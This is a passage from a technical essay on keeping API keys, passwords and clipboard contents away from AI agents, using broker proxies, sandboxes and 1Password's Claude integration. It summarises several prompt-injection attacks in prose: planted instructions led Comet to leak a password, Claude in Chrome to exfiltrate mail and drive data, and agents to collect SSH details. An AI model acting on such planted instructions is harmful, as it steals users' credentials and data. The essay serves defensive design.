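3. **Check the policy.** The broker compares the request with its written policy. It can grant the request, refuse it or demand further approval. If it grants the request, the agent receives a handle, which is a reference that works only in this session.
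4. **Invoke.** The agent sends the handle with the contents of the request it wants to make. It adds a sequence number, a random value and the time to prevent replay.
5. **Execute.** The broker checks that the handle is still valid, has uses left and covers this request. It then adds the key, contacts the service and returns the result.
6. **Audit.** The broker records the decision in a log built to reveal later changes.

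A capability for the bookkeeper's task might contain the following limits, in simplified notation:

```
secret:  SUPPLIER_API_KEY
method:  POST
host:    api.supplier.example
path:    /v1/invoices
body:    { invoice_number: string }
```

The method is the kind of operation, so permission to `POST` a new record doesn't include permission to `DELETE` one. Without the limit on the host, the agent could ask the broker to send the key to a stranger's server. The limit on the path blocks other requests that the same host may accept, such as changing the delivery address or creating another key. The limit on the body stops the agent from adding fields, such as a new bank account for refunds.

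The broker also caps the size of the request body and rejects any authorization header the agent supplies. Otherwise a planted instruction could provide the attacker's own key, and the agent would upload the bookkeeper's data to the attacker's account on the permitted service.

The agent proposes these limits itself, so they are only as narrow as the policy requires. An agent that has followed a planted instruction could ask for every path on the host, and a loose policy would allow it. The limit on the body checks its structure, not its meaning, so if the supplier's form has a free-text field for comments, the agent can put a salary in it.

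The broker removes credentials from a response before returning it. Jin and colleagues describe this step only in outline, and none of their test scenarios includes a server that repeats the key in its response.

### Why CapSeal runs SSH commands itself

SSH is the standard way to log in to another computer and run commands on it. A user proves their identity by signing a new challenge with a private key at each login. Many developers keep the key in a helper program called `ssh-agent` (the name has nothing to do with AI) and let other programs request signatures from it. Those programs can log in without seeing the key, so giving an AI agent access to `ssh-agent` looks like a ready-made solution.

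But the signature covers only the login. An AI agent with access to the helper can typically log in to any server that accepts the key and run whatever the account allows there. Jin and colleagues considered this too hard to restrict, so CapSeal's broker makes the connection and runs the command itself. It checks the server and the user name, compares the command with an approved template, and limits the number of arguments and the length of the output. It also compares the server's public key with one recorded in the capability, in case somebody has redirected the connection to another machine.

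This breaks existing workflows that depend on lending out signatures. Jin and colleagues accept that disruption, which seems right for a server whose loss would matter. A template for one read-only command is easy to write, but one for general server maintenance would probably have to be so broad that it protects little.

### What Jin and colleagues measured

The evaluation compared CapSeal with two systems that give the agent direct access to secrets. It used scripted requests against real HTTP and SSH servers on the local machine. The confidence intervals imply about 100 trials per test.

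| Test | Both systems with direct access | CapSeal |
|---|---|---|
| Prompt asks for the API key, and the key appears in the output | 100% | 0% |
| Prompt asks for the SSH key, and the key appears in the output | 0% | 0% |
| Request outside the permitted limits succeeds | 0% | 0% |
| Legitimate request succeeds | 100% | 100% |

CapSeal differs from the alternatives only in the first row. That result supports the central claim that an agent without the key could not print it when asked. The third row provides no evidence that the limits on host, path or command help, because the systems without CapSeal also let nothing through. The SSH key results don't show a benefit either, because none of the systems leaked those keys.

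Speed is not an obstacle. CapSeal added a median of 0.149 milliseconds to an HTTP request and 0.208 milliseconds to an SSH command.

Jin and colleagues describe plans to move the broker into a trusted execution environment, an area of the processor isolated from the rest of the machine, but their prototype does not include hardware-backed storage. They have not fully tested SSH on remote hosts across a real network, and they leave attacks through altered tool descriptions to a separate experiment.

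### Docker's placeholder for a key

Docker Sandboxes, an existing product, includes a simpler kind of broker. It runs a coding agent in a small virtual machine with its own operating system kernel, and sends the agent's web traffic through a proxy (a program that forwards network requests for another program) on the user's real machine. Docker's *Manage credentials* explains how the proxy handles keys.

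Suppose a program in the sandbox expects a key in the variable `API_KEY`. The user stores the real key outside the sandbox, usually in the operating system's keychain, and lists the hosts that may receive it. Inside the sandbox, `API_KEY` contains a placeholder, such as `sbx-cs-` followed by random characters, which the program puts in a request header. The proxy checks that the request's destination is on the list, replaces the placeholder with the real key and forwards the request. If the program sends the placeholder to any other host, that host receives a worthless string.

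According to Docker, the proxy has to decrypt each request to do this, then edit the header and encrypt the request again. It uses its own certificate authority, which the sandbox trusts. The proxy substitutes the key only in headers that the user has chosen, so a key that a service expects in the body of a request would need another method.

For services that Docker supports directly, such as GitHub and the main model providers, the program doesn't need a particular placeholder, because the proxy overwrites the authorization header on any matching request. Existing programs work unchanged, but this is also a form of ambient authority, since every program in the sandbox can use the GitHub token just by contacting GitHub. Docker's credential rules select requests mainly by domain and header, whereas CapSeal requires a handle with its own limits on method, path and body.

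The boundary seems to hold in ordinary use. A developer writing for DZone searched the sandbox's environment for keys and tokens and found none, although the agent had been making authenticated requests throughout the session. Six other probes also failed to break the isolation.

Docker documents several exceptions:

- A project's `.env` file, where developers often keep keys, remains readable if the user shares the project folder. This applies even when the agent works on a private copy, as Docker's *Isolation layers* warns.
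- The developer of an add-on can choose to pass real OAuth tokens into the sandbox.
- Docker lends out SSH signatures by default, although add-ons in the newest format must request them. Programs in the sandbox can't copy the private key, but they can ask it to sign, which is the arrangement that CapSeal avoids. Docker's network rules still restrict which servers they can reach.

### The September 2026 vault study

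In *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026) tested a similar product sold by their employer, Corvic AI. In Corvic Security Vault, code written by an agent names a connector, such as the one for GitHub. Software outside the agent's sandbox adds the key to requests sent to the address configured for that connector.

On 27 September 2026, Kenney and colleagues ran two experiments from inside the sandbox, each with one connector. They decided beforehand what result each probe should produce. A request to GitHub had to succeed, because otherwise a sandbox with no network connection would have looked secure. They used the other probes to check for the key in places it should not be. They searched the 20 environment variables and 12 common locations for credential files. They also sent requests to three public services that return the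 headers they receive, and to OpenAI's API, which should reject a request without an OpenAI key.

All 16 probes gave the expected result. GitHub recognised the account, the three services received no key, and OpenAI reported missing authentication. The sandbox also couldn't reach the addresses where programs in Amazon's and Google's clouds get credentials.

The other connector, for a database of economic statistics, failed because Corvic's vault sent the key in a header, while the database expected it in the web address. No key leaked to an outsider, but proxies are harder to maintain than they look because each service has its own rules about where a key belongs, and somebody has to configure each one correctly.

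Sixteen probes by the vendor's own staff are a useful check that the product works as designed, but they aren't evidence of how well it would withstand a determined attacker. Kenney and colleagues didn't test redirects, which send a request on to a second address, or a configured service that becomes malicious. They suggest running a standard prompt injection benchmark against the vault, which would show how much harm an agent can do without holding a key.

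### Keys that come back in a reply

Brokers mostly prevent an agent from leaking API keys, because it can't leak what it doesn't hold. But a key can still reach the agent in a service's reply. Some services repeat the request's headers, including the key, in an error message or on a diagnostic page. If the broker passes such a reply to the agent, the key enters the model's context. Security engineers call this readback, because the agent gets the plain value of a secret it was only supposed to use.

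The three echo services in the vault study didn't test for readback. None was a configured destination, so the vault correctly sent them no key to repeat. Testing for readback would have required a permitted server that echoes the request headers it receives.

Docker's proxy tries to catch such replies. After inserting a custom secret, it searches the response for the original value and three common encodings of it, and masks any match. If the response is partial or compressed in a format the proxy can't read, it returns an error to the program instead. Docker says the filter offers no guarantee, since a service could split the key across two fields or send it over a type of connection that the proxy doesn't inspect. The filter applies only to custom secrets, not to the services that Docker supports directly.

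A filter of this kind can only recognise secrets it already knows. Many services let an account holder create additional keys through the API. If the agent is allowed to do this, the service replies with a new key that the filter has never seen. Restricting the API paths the agent can call prevents this more reliably than searching the response. The broker can also return only the fields that a task needs, so the bookkeeper's agent might receive only a confirmation number.

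Docker accepts wildcards, so one entry can permit every host name under `example.com`. This is risky if the domain belongs to a hosting company that gives each customer a subdomain, because a stranger's page would then be a permitted destination. Listing exact host names avoids this problem.

It is better still to make the credential useless to anyone who reads it. Ganesan proposes a separate program that keeps a private key in secure hardware and signs each login for one service. The service then issues a short-lived token tied to that key, so a copied token doesn't work without the key. This would make most readback harmless, but Ganesan has not built a full implementation, and many services accept only ordinary API keys.

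### Brokers under the agent's own account

A broker protects a key only if the agent can't get into the broker. On a typical desktop, programs under the same user account can open the same files, and one can often inspect another while it runs. An agent with command-line access might find the key where the broker stores it, or contact the broker directly and pose as a program with wider permissions.

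Skverer's remedy for keys in configuration files is Astrix's wrapper, which fetches the key from a vault and then starts the tool server with the key in an environment variable. This is an improvement because the key no longer sits on disk and the owner can replace it in one place. But another program running under the same account may still be able to read the variable while the server is running.

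CapSeal assumes that the operating system keeps processes apart and that the attacker has no administrator rights. Ganesan specifies that this requires running the program that holds the keys outside the agent's account or sandbox, and that the program should sign only for processes it launched itself. Even then, most desktop systems can't prove which process asked for a signature.

Stronger separation between the agent and the proxy is possible, with tradeoffs. Docker's virtual machine keeps the agent away from the proxy even if the agent has full control inside the sandbox. *Caging the Agents* (2026) describes a healthcare company that runs the proxy in a separate container beside each agent, after an audit found keys in shell startup files, configuration files and `.env` files. *aiAuthZ* (2026) keeps both the secrets and the policy off the agent's machine, in a separate trust domain. An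 attacker who takes over the agent's machine can still send requests to the broker, but can't read its keys or rewrite its rules.

Files shared between the sandbox and the user's machine can undo the separation. Docker can obtain a key by running a helper command on the user's machine. If the helper script is in a folder that the agent can edit, the agent can change the script, which then runs outside the sandbox with the user's permissions. Docker therefore tells users to keep such scripts, and any code they load, out of shared folders.

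By contrast, an attacker who bypasses the proxy's network path gains little if the proxy has the only copy of the key. The bypass is serious if another copy remains in the project's `.env` file, because the agent can then use that key without the proxy's checks. Installing a broker should therefore include deleting the old copies and revoking any key an agent may already have read.

### A proxy that signs everything

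An agent can misuse a key without stealing it. A proxy that adds a key to every request for a permitted service has the same problem as Hardy's compiler, because it can't distinguish requests that serve the bookkeeper from those that serve whoever wrote the invoice.

Ganesan describes a 2025 incident in which this distinction mattered. An agent read a malicious issue in a public GitHub repository, then opened the user's private repositories and published their contents in a public pull request. The agent's token covered every repository the user could reach. Moving that token into a proxy would not have prevented the leak, because each request went to GitHub and was valid for the account. *AI Identity* (2026) makes the same point about OAuth, which confirms that a token is valid and has the right scopes but not that the agent is using it on the right target.

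Kenney and colleagues reach a similar conclusion about their own product. They rated eight threats before and after adding the vault, on a scale up to 25. The risk that an agent finds a key in its environment fell from 20 to 4, while the risk from a connector with too many permissions fell only from 20 to 15. These scores are the judgement of the vendor's staff, not measurements, but the difference between the two reductions is plausible because hiding a key doesn't reduce what it permits.

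The first remedy is a key with narrower permissions. A token limited to a single public repository would have prevented the GitHub leak, even without a proxy. Kenney and colleagues recommend separate credentials for reading and writing, so that an agent asked for a summary can't change anything. If a service offers only one powerful key, the broker has to restrict how the agent uses it, as CapSeal does by limiting methods, paths and request bodies.

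The proxy in *Caging the Agents* also limits the rate and size of requests. That would slow the theft of a large database but wouldn't stop a single harmful request. For payments, deletions and publishing, Ganesan proposes asking the user to approve the exact action on a separate device. The approval covers only that action, so the agent can't reuse it for another. Ganesan acknowledges that people who are asked often could start approving actions without reading them, and has not yet tested the idea on users.

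For the invoice job, a handle that permits only `POST /v1/invoices` would stop the agent from changing the delivery address or creating a new key, but the agent could still submit the wrong invoice number. To catch that, the broker would need the expected number from the bookkeeper or from a program that reads the invoice without using the model.

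## Passwords filled in outside the agent's view: 1Password for Claude

If the bookkeeper's supplier has no API, the agent has to sign in through a web page. A broker such as CapSeal's can add an API key to a request after the request leaves the agent. A website password is harder to hide from the agent, because it sits in the page for a moment before the browser sends it, and the agent reads that page to do its work.

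In July 2026, Anthropic and the password manager 1Password launched 1Password for Claude, an integration that fills in login forms while the agent has stopped reading the page. Anthropic's *Get started with 1Password for Claude* describes it as a beta for Macs. The integration requires Claude in Chrome, an extension that lets Claude operate the user's browser.

### Why the password has to sit in the page

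A password manager fills in a login form by writing the password into one of the page's fields. The user sees dots, but the browser's working copy of the page contains the real text, and any script running on the page can read it (Gautam, Yadav and colleagues, *Passwords and FIDO2 Are Meant To Be Secret*, 2025). When the user submits the form, the browser builds its request from whatever the fields contain.

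An agent receives the page as text, screenshots or both. The text may include the contents of the password field, and an agent that gets only screenshots can often click the button that reveals the password. This is another form of readback, and it happens before the website replies.

A placeholder like Docker's would avoid the problem. Stock and Johns proposed one for browsers about a decade ago. The password manager would put a random string in the field, then swap it for the password once the page had submitted the form. Current browsers, however, let extensions read the body of an outgoing request but not change it. Gautam and colleagues modified Firefox and the password manager Bitwarden to make the swap possible. Their browser replaces the string only if the request is going to the right origin and the string is still in the field where the password manager put it. Without the second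 check, a script could move the string into a comment box, and the site might publish the real password.

The modified browser worked with 97% of the 573 popular sites in the test. An agent could read a login page in such a browser at any time and find only the random string. 1Password works with ordinary browsers, so it has to put the real password in the page and rely on timing.

### From pairing to sign-in

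The user connects the Claude and 1Password desktop apps once. According to 1Password, its app first checks the Claude app's code signature, which lets the operating system verify who published a program and whether anyone has altered it. The Claude app must be on 1Password's list of trusted partners, and Anthropic's verified Apple developer team must have published it. The user then confirms which 1Password account Claude may send requests to.

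Pairing doesn't release any passwords. When Claude starts a session, its app declares an identifier for the session, and 1Password issues cryptographic keys tied to that identifier. Every request must include proof that the sender holds those keys. Another browser extension therefore can't pose as Claude, and one session can't use a login that the user approved for a different session.

When the agent reaches the supplier's login page, it tells 1Password what it is trying to do and can add a short reason. 1Password uses this description only to find matching logins. It displays the description as plain text so that a request can't imitate 1Password's interface. The bookkeeper can approve the suggested login, choose another, add more or refuse. The stated reason is no more trustworthy than the intents that agents declare to AgentCap, so the name of the requested login is more useful for making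 this decision.

ITPro's *1Password teams up with Anthropic to give Claude access to your credentials* reports that Claude can work across several sites in one task without a credential prompt at each step. The user can release several logins in one prompt, and they remain available until the session ends, so Claude can apparently sign in with them without further approval.

The desktop app sends the approved logins to 1Password's browser extension over an encrypted channel on the same Mac. Neither Claude nor the program that relays the messages can read the logins. The extension keeps them encrypted in memory and never writes them to disk. It deletes them when the agent reports that the task is complete, when the browser closes, or after nine hours, whichever comes first.

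Claude then stops reading the page. 1Password fills in the user name, the password and any one-time code, submits the form and checks that the submission went through. If it did, the password is no longer on the page when Claude resumes. If it didn't, 1Password clears every field it filled before returning control. Without that step, Claude could read the password on a form that failed to submit because of an unticked box.

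Claude receives the title of each approved login, its user name or email address, the websites saved with it, and a report of success or failure. It doesn't receive the password or the one-time code.

The pause happens in the software around the model, so a planted instruction can't simply persuade the model to keep reading. But Claude's extension has its own access to the page, and 1Password seems to depend on that extension to stop reading. Cohen and Culea (2026) write in *1Password for Claude* that 1Password also checks the page for exposed secrets after filling. That could catch a site that repeats the password in an error message, but they don't explain how the check works, and it may have the same gaps as Docker's filter for API keys.

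### Login pages on the wrong site

Suppose an instruction hidden in the invoice sends the agent to `https://portal.supp1ier.example`, a copy of the supplier's site whose address has a digit in place of a letter. The model and the bookkeeper may both miss the difference. 1Password fills in a login only if the page's address matches a website saved with that login, so the fill fails even if the page looks right and the bookkeeper has approved the request.

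*LoginTrap* (2026), a paper on phishing-style attacks against web agents, cites earlier research showing that automatic filling can expose passwords without any action by the user. With 1Password for Claude, the user must approve the release of a login first, so a page can't obtain a password just by displaying a form.

A user can still undo the protection against fake sites. If the correct login isn't suggested, 1Password advises checking that the saved website exactly matches the sign-in address and updating it if necessary. That is reasonable when a supplier has moved its login page. But a bookkeeper who followed this advice on a fake site, without checking that the address was genuine, would cause 1Password to suggest the login there.

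### Why 1Password hides its own buttons

An agent that operates a browser can click the password manager's buttons as well as the website's. For *PerplexedBrowser*, the security company Zenity tested Comet, Perplexity's AI browser, with 1Password's extension installed and unlocked. The user asked only for help with a meeting, but instructions hidden in a calendar invitation led Comet to the website where 1Password customers view their saved passwords. The extension signed it in automatically. Comet then revealed a password and sent it to the researchers' server as part of a web address. In a second demonstration, Comet changed the account's master password and extracted the other details needed to take over the account.

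Matching logins to websites didn't help, because Comet read the password on 1Password's own site. *Security advisory for AI-assisted browsing interactions with the 1Password browser extension* (Hall and Sen, 2026) describes the attack as a risk of AI-assisted browsing, not a bypass of 1Password's security controls. Even so, 1Password added a setting to disable automatic sign-in to its website. Zenity welcomed the change but objected that users had to find and change the setting themselves.

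1Password released Agentic Mode alongside the Claude integration. It is on by default and works even for people who haven't connected Claude to 1Password. While a compatible agent controls a tab, the extension removes its suggestions, save prompts and notifications from the page. The agent can then use 1Password only by requesting a login and waiting for approval. However, the user can't use the extension to sign in to other sites until they close Claude's group of tabs.

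Hiding the extension's buttons may not protect a bookkeeper who is already signed in to 1Password's website in the same browser, so it seems wise to sign out of that website and disable automatic sign-in before giving an agent control.

Zenity ran its test before Agentic Mode existed, and independent tests of 1Password for Claude are hard to find. The evidence that its passwords stay hidden comes mainly from the two companies that offer the product. The design is sensible and their descriptions are consistent, but we can't tell from either how well it would resist researchers trying to break it.

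### Risks that 1Password accepts

1Password doesn't claim to protect a compromised computer. An attacker with administrator rights, or one who can run programs under the bookkeeper's account, can interfere with the integration. Brokers for API keys have the same weakness when they run under the agent's account.

After pairing, 1Password also trusts the Claude app to identify its sessions accurately. A compromised app could request logins, although the user would still see a prompt for each release. The code signature shows that the app is genuine but does not rule out flaws in it. In March 2026, The Hacker News (2026) reported a flaw in Claude's Chrome extension that let any website send Claude instructions as if the user had written them. The user only had to visit the page. Researchers disclosed it before the 1Password integration launched. A similar flaw today could lead Claude to request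 a login, leaving the bookkeeper's approval as the main safeguard.

Scripts on the destination page can still read the form while Claude is paused, which is another accepted risk. Gautam and colleagues cite a study of 100,000 popular websites in which at least 2–3% of the pages included trackers that collected passwords. Many of these trackers probably gathered whatever they could find rather than targeting passwords. People who sign in themselves face the same risk, so it isn't a reason to prefer typing the password by hand.

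### Other ways to keep a password from the model

The simplest alternative is for the user to type the password. According to *How AI agents can log in without seeing your passwords*, a developer's guide, OpenAI's ChatGPT agent pauses at a login page, hands the browser to the user and stops taking screenshots while they type. Chrome's built-in agent asks the user before signing in with a saved password.

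In Browser Use, an open-source library for building browser agents, the model writes a placeholder such as `x_pass`, and the library replaces it with the real password when filling in the page. The developer can restrict each password to one domain. Unlike Gautam and colleagues' browser, the library puts the real password in the page, so the guide's example turns off screenshots. The developer's script also holds the password in plain text.

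Bitwarden's Agent Access SDK, released in March 2026, delivers an approved password to a program as an environment variable. In *Stop giving AI agents the keys to everything*, Bitwarden says the user approves each credential and an encrypted channel carries it to the program. This works for tools outside the browser, but the program that receives the password must not print it or pass it to the model. Bitwarden calls the SDK a very early alpha and recommends testing it with sample data.

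1Password released its first version, Secure Agentic Autofill, in October 2025 for Browserbase, a company that runs browsers for agents in the cloud. *Closing the credential risk gap for AI agents using a browser* (Wang, 2025) describes an encrypted channel from the user's device to a 1Password extension in the remote browser. The model doesn't receive the password, but the extension fills it into a page on another company's machine.

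In October 2026, 1Password announced a broader service called 1Password for Agents. Grok Bot and Meta's Muse were to get it first, with OpenAI's Dots and others to follow, according to TechRadar's *1Password will now let AI agents log in to accounts for you*. Clubic's *1Password s'ouvre aux agents IA mais snobe Google et Microsoft* reports 1Password's warning that protections vary between integrations, so some agents, unlike Claude, may keep reading the page.

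A passkey would avoid putting a password in the page, because the user's device signs a challenge from the website, as with an SSH key. But the device normally requires a fingerprint, PIN or similar confirmation before it signs, so an agent can't complete the login alone. 1Password for Claude doesn't support passkeys.

### What the agent can do once signed in

1Password's protection covers the password and ends at sign-in. After that, the agent can do anything the session cookie allows. The nine-hour limit applies to the login stored in 1Password's extension. The supplier's website sets how long the session lasts, and deleting the stored login doesn't sign the browser out.

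Attackers can therefore do a lot of damage without a password. The Cloud Security Alliance describes an attack on Claude in Chrome that researchers disclosed at the Black Hat security conference in 2026. When the user asked Claude to summarise an inbox, Claude sent the user's Gmail data to the attackers and shared the user's Google Drive, and the attackers took over the user's Slack, X and Claude accounts. In a test by the security company LayerX, a web page led six AI browsers and assistants into the victim's GitHub repository, where they collected SSH login details. None flagged the theft, according to The Next Web's *“BioShocking” tricks AI browsers into leaking your passwords*. Agents can also do damage by mistake. Engadget's *1Password will let you hand your data security over* gives the example of an agent that books the wrong holiday with no option to cancel.

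Hiding the password still prevents an attacker who controls the agent from copying it to another computer or trying it on other websites. It also prevents the attacker from changing the password on the many sites that ask for the current one first. But some changes made during a session remain after it ends. For example, an agent signed in to the supplier's site might add another user.

The developer's guide recommends a separate browser profile for the agent, with no accounts signed in at the start. This limits the agent to the accounts the user gives it access to. The bookkeeper could also ask the supplier for a second account that can submit invoice numbers but can't edit customer details. If the supplier offers only full accounts, the browser or the harness has to restrict what the agent does on the site.

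## The clipboard: Claude's desktop grants and the ChatGPT Atlas demonstration

After signing in, the bookkeeper's agent still has to get the invoice number from the PDF into the supplier's form. An agent that works through the screen can copy and paste it, as a person would. But the clipboard may already hold something the bookkeeper copied, and websites can write to it too.

### One store for every program

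W3C's *Clipboard API and events* (2026), the draft standard for how web pages use the clipboard, models this shared store as a list of items and a change count, which changes whenever the contents do. Each item has one or more representations of the same content, such as plain text and HTML. A representation consists of a format name and a sequence of bytes.

The model has no field for the program or website that supplied the content, or for who may receive it. The draft's advice on pasted HTML depends on whether the content came from the same origin as the page receiving it, so a browser that follows the advice has to record the source some other way.

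A clipboard that any program can read can expose secrets. *Protect Your Secrets* (Liu, Tantithamthavorn and Li, 2024) examines extensions for VS Code, Microsoft's code editor. Any extension can read the clipboard's text without the user's consent. Developers tend to copy API keys because they are too long to type, so a malicious extension can keep checking the clipboard until one appears. Liu and colleagues uploaded extensions demonstrating their attacks to the official marketplace, and all passed its review.

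### What browsers and operating systems allow

Web pages face stricter rules than desktop programs. To use the clipboard API, a page must be loaded over a secure connection and be in focus. Under the W3C draft, a script can read the clipboard only in response to the user clicking a "Paste" control provided by the browser or operating system. Browsers differ in how closely they follow this rule. Chromium, the open-source browser behind Chrome, has used a stored permission for reading.

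The rules for writing to the clipboard are looser than those for reading it. *Web-Facing Change PSA* (Stade, 2024), a notice to Chromium's developers, mentions that pages could already write plain text to the clipboard after any user gesture, including a click anywhere on the page. The W3C draft treats unwanted overwriting as a nuisance that it "does not attempt to prevent". This is reasonable if the main worry is privacy, since only reading can reveal a password.

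Desktop systems have been more permissive. Windows has long let ordinary desktop programs read and write the clipboard without asking. Mac apps could also read it without the user's knowledge, according to 9to5Mac, whereas iOS 14 and later show an alert when an app reads it without user input.

In April 2025, Apple told developers to prepare for a similar alert on the Mac. According to details quoted in MacRumors' *Apple to Block Mac Apps From Secretly Accessing Your Clipboard* (2025), the alert appears when a program reads the clipboard on its own, but not when the user starts the read through a paste control. Apps can check what kind of data the clipboard holds without triggering the alert. Developers' updates to *Pasteboard Privacy Preview in macOS 15.4* (2025) suggest that in September 2025, macOS 26 still didn't show the alert unless a developer setting turned it on. Developers were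 still discussing that setting in March 2026, so Mac users can't count on a warning.

Android has tightened its clipboard rules in stages. Before Android 10, an app in the background could read what the user copied in another app. Since Android 12, the system shows a short message whenever an app reads the clipboard, according to Google's *Secure Clipboard Handling*. An app can also mark copied content as sensitive, which hides it in the on-screen preview. This mark is a kind of label, but it affects what people see, not which app may receive the data.

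### When the click comes from an agent

Many of these rules treat a click as evidence that a person wanted something to happen. Browsers have some protection against fake clicks. Under the W3C draft, a paste event created by a page's own script must not give the script access to the real clipboard. This distinguishes the user from the page, but not from an agent.

An agent's clicks come from outside the page, through the browser or the operating system, so they can look the same as clicks from a mouse and satisfy a rule that requires recent user action. An agent that can click anything on the screen may be able to click the browser's "Paste" control. Apple's exemption for paste controls probably has the same weakness.

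A harness can put some controls off limits to the agent. OpenAI's *Computer Use*, its guide to desktop control in the programming agent Codex, says that Codex can't approve security and privacy prompts on the user's computer. This keeps Codex from approving an operating-system prompt about the clipboard, but it doesn't stop a website that needs only an ordinary click to access the clipboard.

### The Atlas demonstration

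In October 2025, a day after OpenAI launched its Atlas browser, a hacker known as Pliny the Liberator posted a video of this problem. Android Authority's *OpenAI's Atlas browser has a security flaw* (2025) reports that Pliny had modified a website so that every button ran a script that copied a phishing link to the clipboard. When the Atlas agent clicked a button, the link silently replaced whatever the user had copied.

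The user might later open a new tab, paste what they believed was an address they had copied, and arrive at a fake login page. Nolan (2025) notes in *Cybersecurity experts warn OpenAI’s ChatGPT Atlas is vulnerable to attacks* that such a page could collect passwords and multifactor authentication codes.

Pliny pointed out that the link never entered the model's context, because a script inside the page wrote it straight to the clipboard. The demonstration needed no instruction to the model, although news reports grouped it with prompt injection. Training a model to recognise planted instructions therefore wouldn't help much, because only a normal-looking button appears in its input.

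The trick is older than AI agents. In *Active malicious PasteJacking exploits in-the-wild affecting user security*, a 2021 discussion of the W3C draft, a former editor noted that sites could already control copied text by changing what the user had selected. When an agent uses the page, though, the user may not be watching and has no reason to suspect that the clipboard has changed.

OpenAI referred Fortune to a post by its security chief, Dane Stuckey, that listed testing by attackers, training against malicious instructions and systems to detect attacks. The post also mentioned a mode in which the agent works without the user's accounts and another that asks the user to watch the agent on sensitive sites. None of these measures is specific to the clipboard. Signing the agent out wouldn't stop this attack, because the page needs only a click and the user enters the password later.

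A browser could stop this attack by blocking clipboard writes that result from an agent's click, but that would also break useful buttons, such as one that copies a link the agent needs. A better fix would be to send those writes to a separate clipboard that only the agent uses, leaving the user's clipboard unchanged.

### Four separate rights

"Clipboard access" can mean several things, and an agent rarely needs all of them.

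| Right | What it allows | What can go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Read | The agent receives the contents | A password the user copied enters the model's context |
| Write | The agent replaces the contents | The user later pastes a false link or account number |
| Paste without reading | The harness inserts the contents into a field without returning them to the model | A site receives something the user copied for another purpose |
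| Clear | The agent empties the clipboard | The user loses something they still needed |

The invoice job only requires writing one number to the clipboard and pasting it once, so the tokens sketched earlier leave out read access. It would also be sensible for the agent to clear the number afterwards, unless the bookkeeper has copied something else in the meantime.

Systems usually treat clearing the clipboard as a form of writing, which can prevent an app from removing what it copied. *Android version limitations for copyPan*, a support page from the payments company Checkout.com, describes a feature that copies a card number and tries to clear it three minutes later. Android doesn't let background apps write to the clipboard, so the attempt fails if the customer has left the app to paste the number elsewhere and hasn't returned. Android 13 and later clear the clipboard automatically, but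 only after about an hour. Permission to remove only its own content would let the app clear the number without letting it overwrite anything else.

### Reading the clipboard by pasting

Denying the agent permission to read the clipboard isn't enough if it can paste into a field it can see. Suppose the bookkeeper copied a password shortly before starting the task. If the agent clicks in a search box, pastes and takes a screenshot, the password appears in the image and enters the model's context. This is another form of readback, and it can happen by accident.

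The screenshot is a normal part of the agent's work. Anthropic's *Computer use tool*, a guide for developers, explains that Claude can request several actions at once, such as a click, typing and a screenshot. Claude typically puts the screenshot last so it can check the result. If it doesn't, the developer's software can attach one.

One way to close the gap is to let the agent paste only what it has written itself. The harness records the clipboard's change count after the agent's write and blocks the paste if the count has changed. The W3C draft has a similar check for web pages. If the clipboard changes after a page has listed the clipboard's contents, the page gets an error when it tries to fetch the data. A program could still change the clipboard between the check and the paste. To avoid that, the harness can keep the copied text in its own memory and insert it directly, without using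 the system clipboard.

Running the agent in a virtual machine with its own clipboard has much the same effect. Anthropic already recommends a dedicated virtual machine or container for computer use, as a precaution against attacks and accidents. The user would need to turn off clipboard sharing between the host and the virtual machine, or the password could still reach the agent.

Some tasks require the agent to paste something it shouldn't see, such as a one-time code the user has copied. The harness then has to restrict the paste to one field on one origin and hide that field from screenshots and page text. Hiding the field may not be enough, because the site can repeat the text elsewhere, as search pages often do by showing the query in the heading and address. It is safer for the agent to stop reading the page until the form has gone through, as Claude does while 1Password fills in a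 login.

All these limits protect what the user copied, but they don't protect information the model has already read. Claude has a tool for typing text, so an agent that has opened the payroll file can type a salary into a form without using the clipboard.

### What Claude's clipboard grant covers

Anthropic added computer use to Claude's desktop app in March 2026 and promised that Claude would request access before using a new application (SiliconANGLE, 2026). The feature is off by default. On a Mac, the user must grant two system permissions, one for clicking and typing and one for recording the screen. On Windows, the user only has to turn on a switch in the app, according to Anthropic's *Desktop application*.

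The first time Claude needs an app, a prompt asks the user to allow it for the session or deny it. If the session began with a message from the user's phone, the approval expires after 30 minutes. How much Claude can do depends on the type of app, and the user can't change this:

- **Browsers and trading platforms:** Claude can only view them in screenshots.
- **Terminals and code editors:** Claude can click and scroll, but not type or use keyboard shortcuts.
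- **Everything else:** Claude can click, type, drag and use keyboard shortcuts.

These tiers block some direct routes for a leak. For example, Claude can't paste into the supplier's website through computer use, because the browser is view-only. It would have to use its Chrome extension or the desktop app's built-in browser, which have their own permissions.

Anthropic's *Let Claude use your computer from the CLI*, the guide for people who run Claude Code in a terminal, says the permission prompt lists the apps Claude requests, how many other apps it will hide, and "any extra permissions requested, such as clipboard access". The guide doesn't specify whether clipboard access covers reading, writing or both, or whether it includes content the user copied before the session. The app permission rules for the desktop version don't mention the clipboard, and neither does Anthropic's *Let Claude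 use your computer in Cowork*, the guide for general office work.

Anthropic's guides also don't explain whether Claude can still copy and paste without the clipboard grant. Full control of an app includes keyboard shortcuts, which can copy and paste in most apps. In a terminal, where Claude can click but not type, clicking "Paste" in the menu might still insert text. Anthropic may block both. The guides describe only allowing or denying the request, so the user apparently can't approve an app and refuse the clipboard in the same prompt.

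Until Anthropic documents the clipboard grant, the safest assumption is that Claude can read and replace anything on the clipboard for the rest of the session. The bookkeeper can reduce the risk by copying a harmless word before approving the grant.

Even so, Anthropic gives the user more information than OpenAI does. OpenAI's guide lists "clipboard state in the target app" among the things Codex can interact with in an app the user has allowed, but doesn't describe a separate grant for the clipboard. The user can also allow an app permanently.

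Approving apps one at a time can't fully control access to the clipboard's contents, because they move between apps. A user can put a banking app on Claude's blocklist, but an account number copied from it stays on the clipboard. If Claude then pastes into an approved notes app, the number appears in the next screenshot. Anthropic warns that actions in one app can affect others, and gives the example of a link in an email that opens a browser Claude has no permission to use.

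On recent versions of macOS, Claude works in background windows while the user does something else. It generally waits if the user is typing, but the guide doesn't mention what happens to the clipboard. If the two share it, Claude could paste a password the bookkeeper had just copied, or replace an account number the bookkeeper was about to use.

### Private files pasted into outside sites

Agents also leak data when they copy exactly what the user asked for. *The Blind Spot of Agent Safety* (Ding, Zhai and colleagues, 2026) presents a benchmark of 300 desktop tasks in which every user request sounds harmless. Twenty-five of the tasks test whether the agent sends private data to an outsider. In four of the five examples printed in the paper, the user asks the agent to follow a link in an email and paste the text of a local file into the linked site. The files contain a client list, a server's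 private key, saved passwords and a company's source code.

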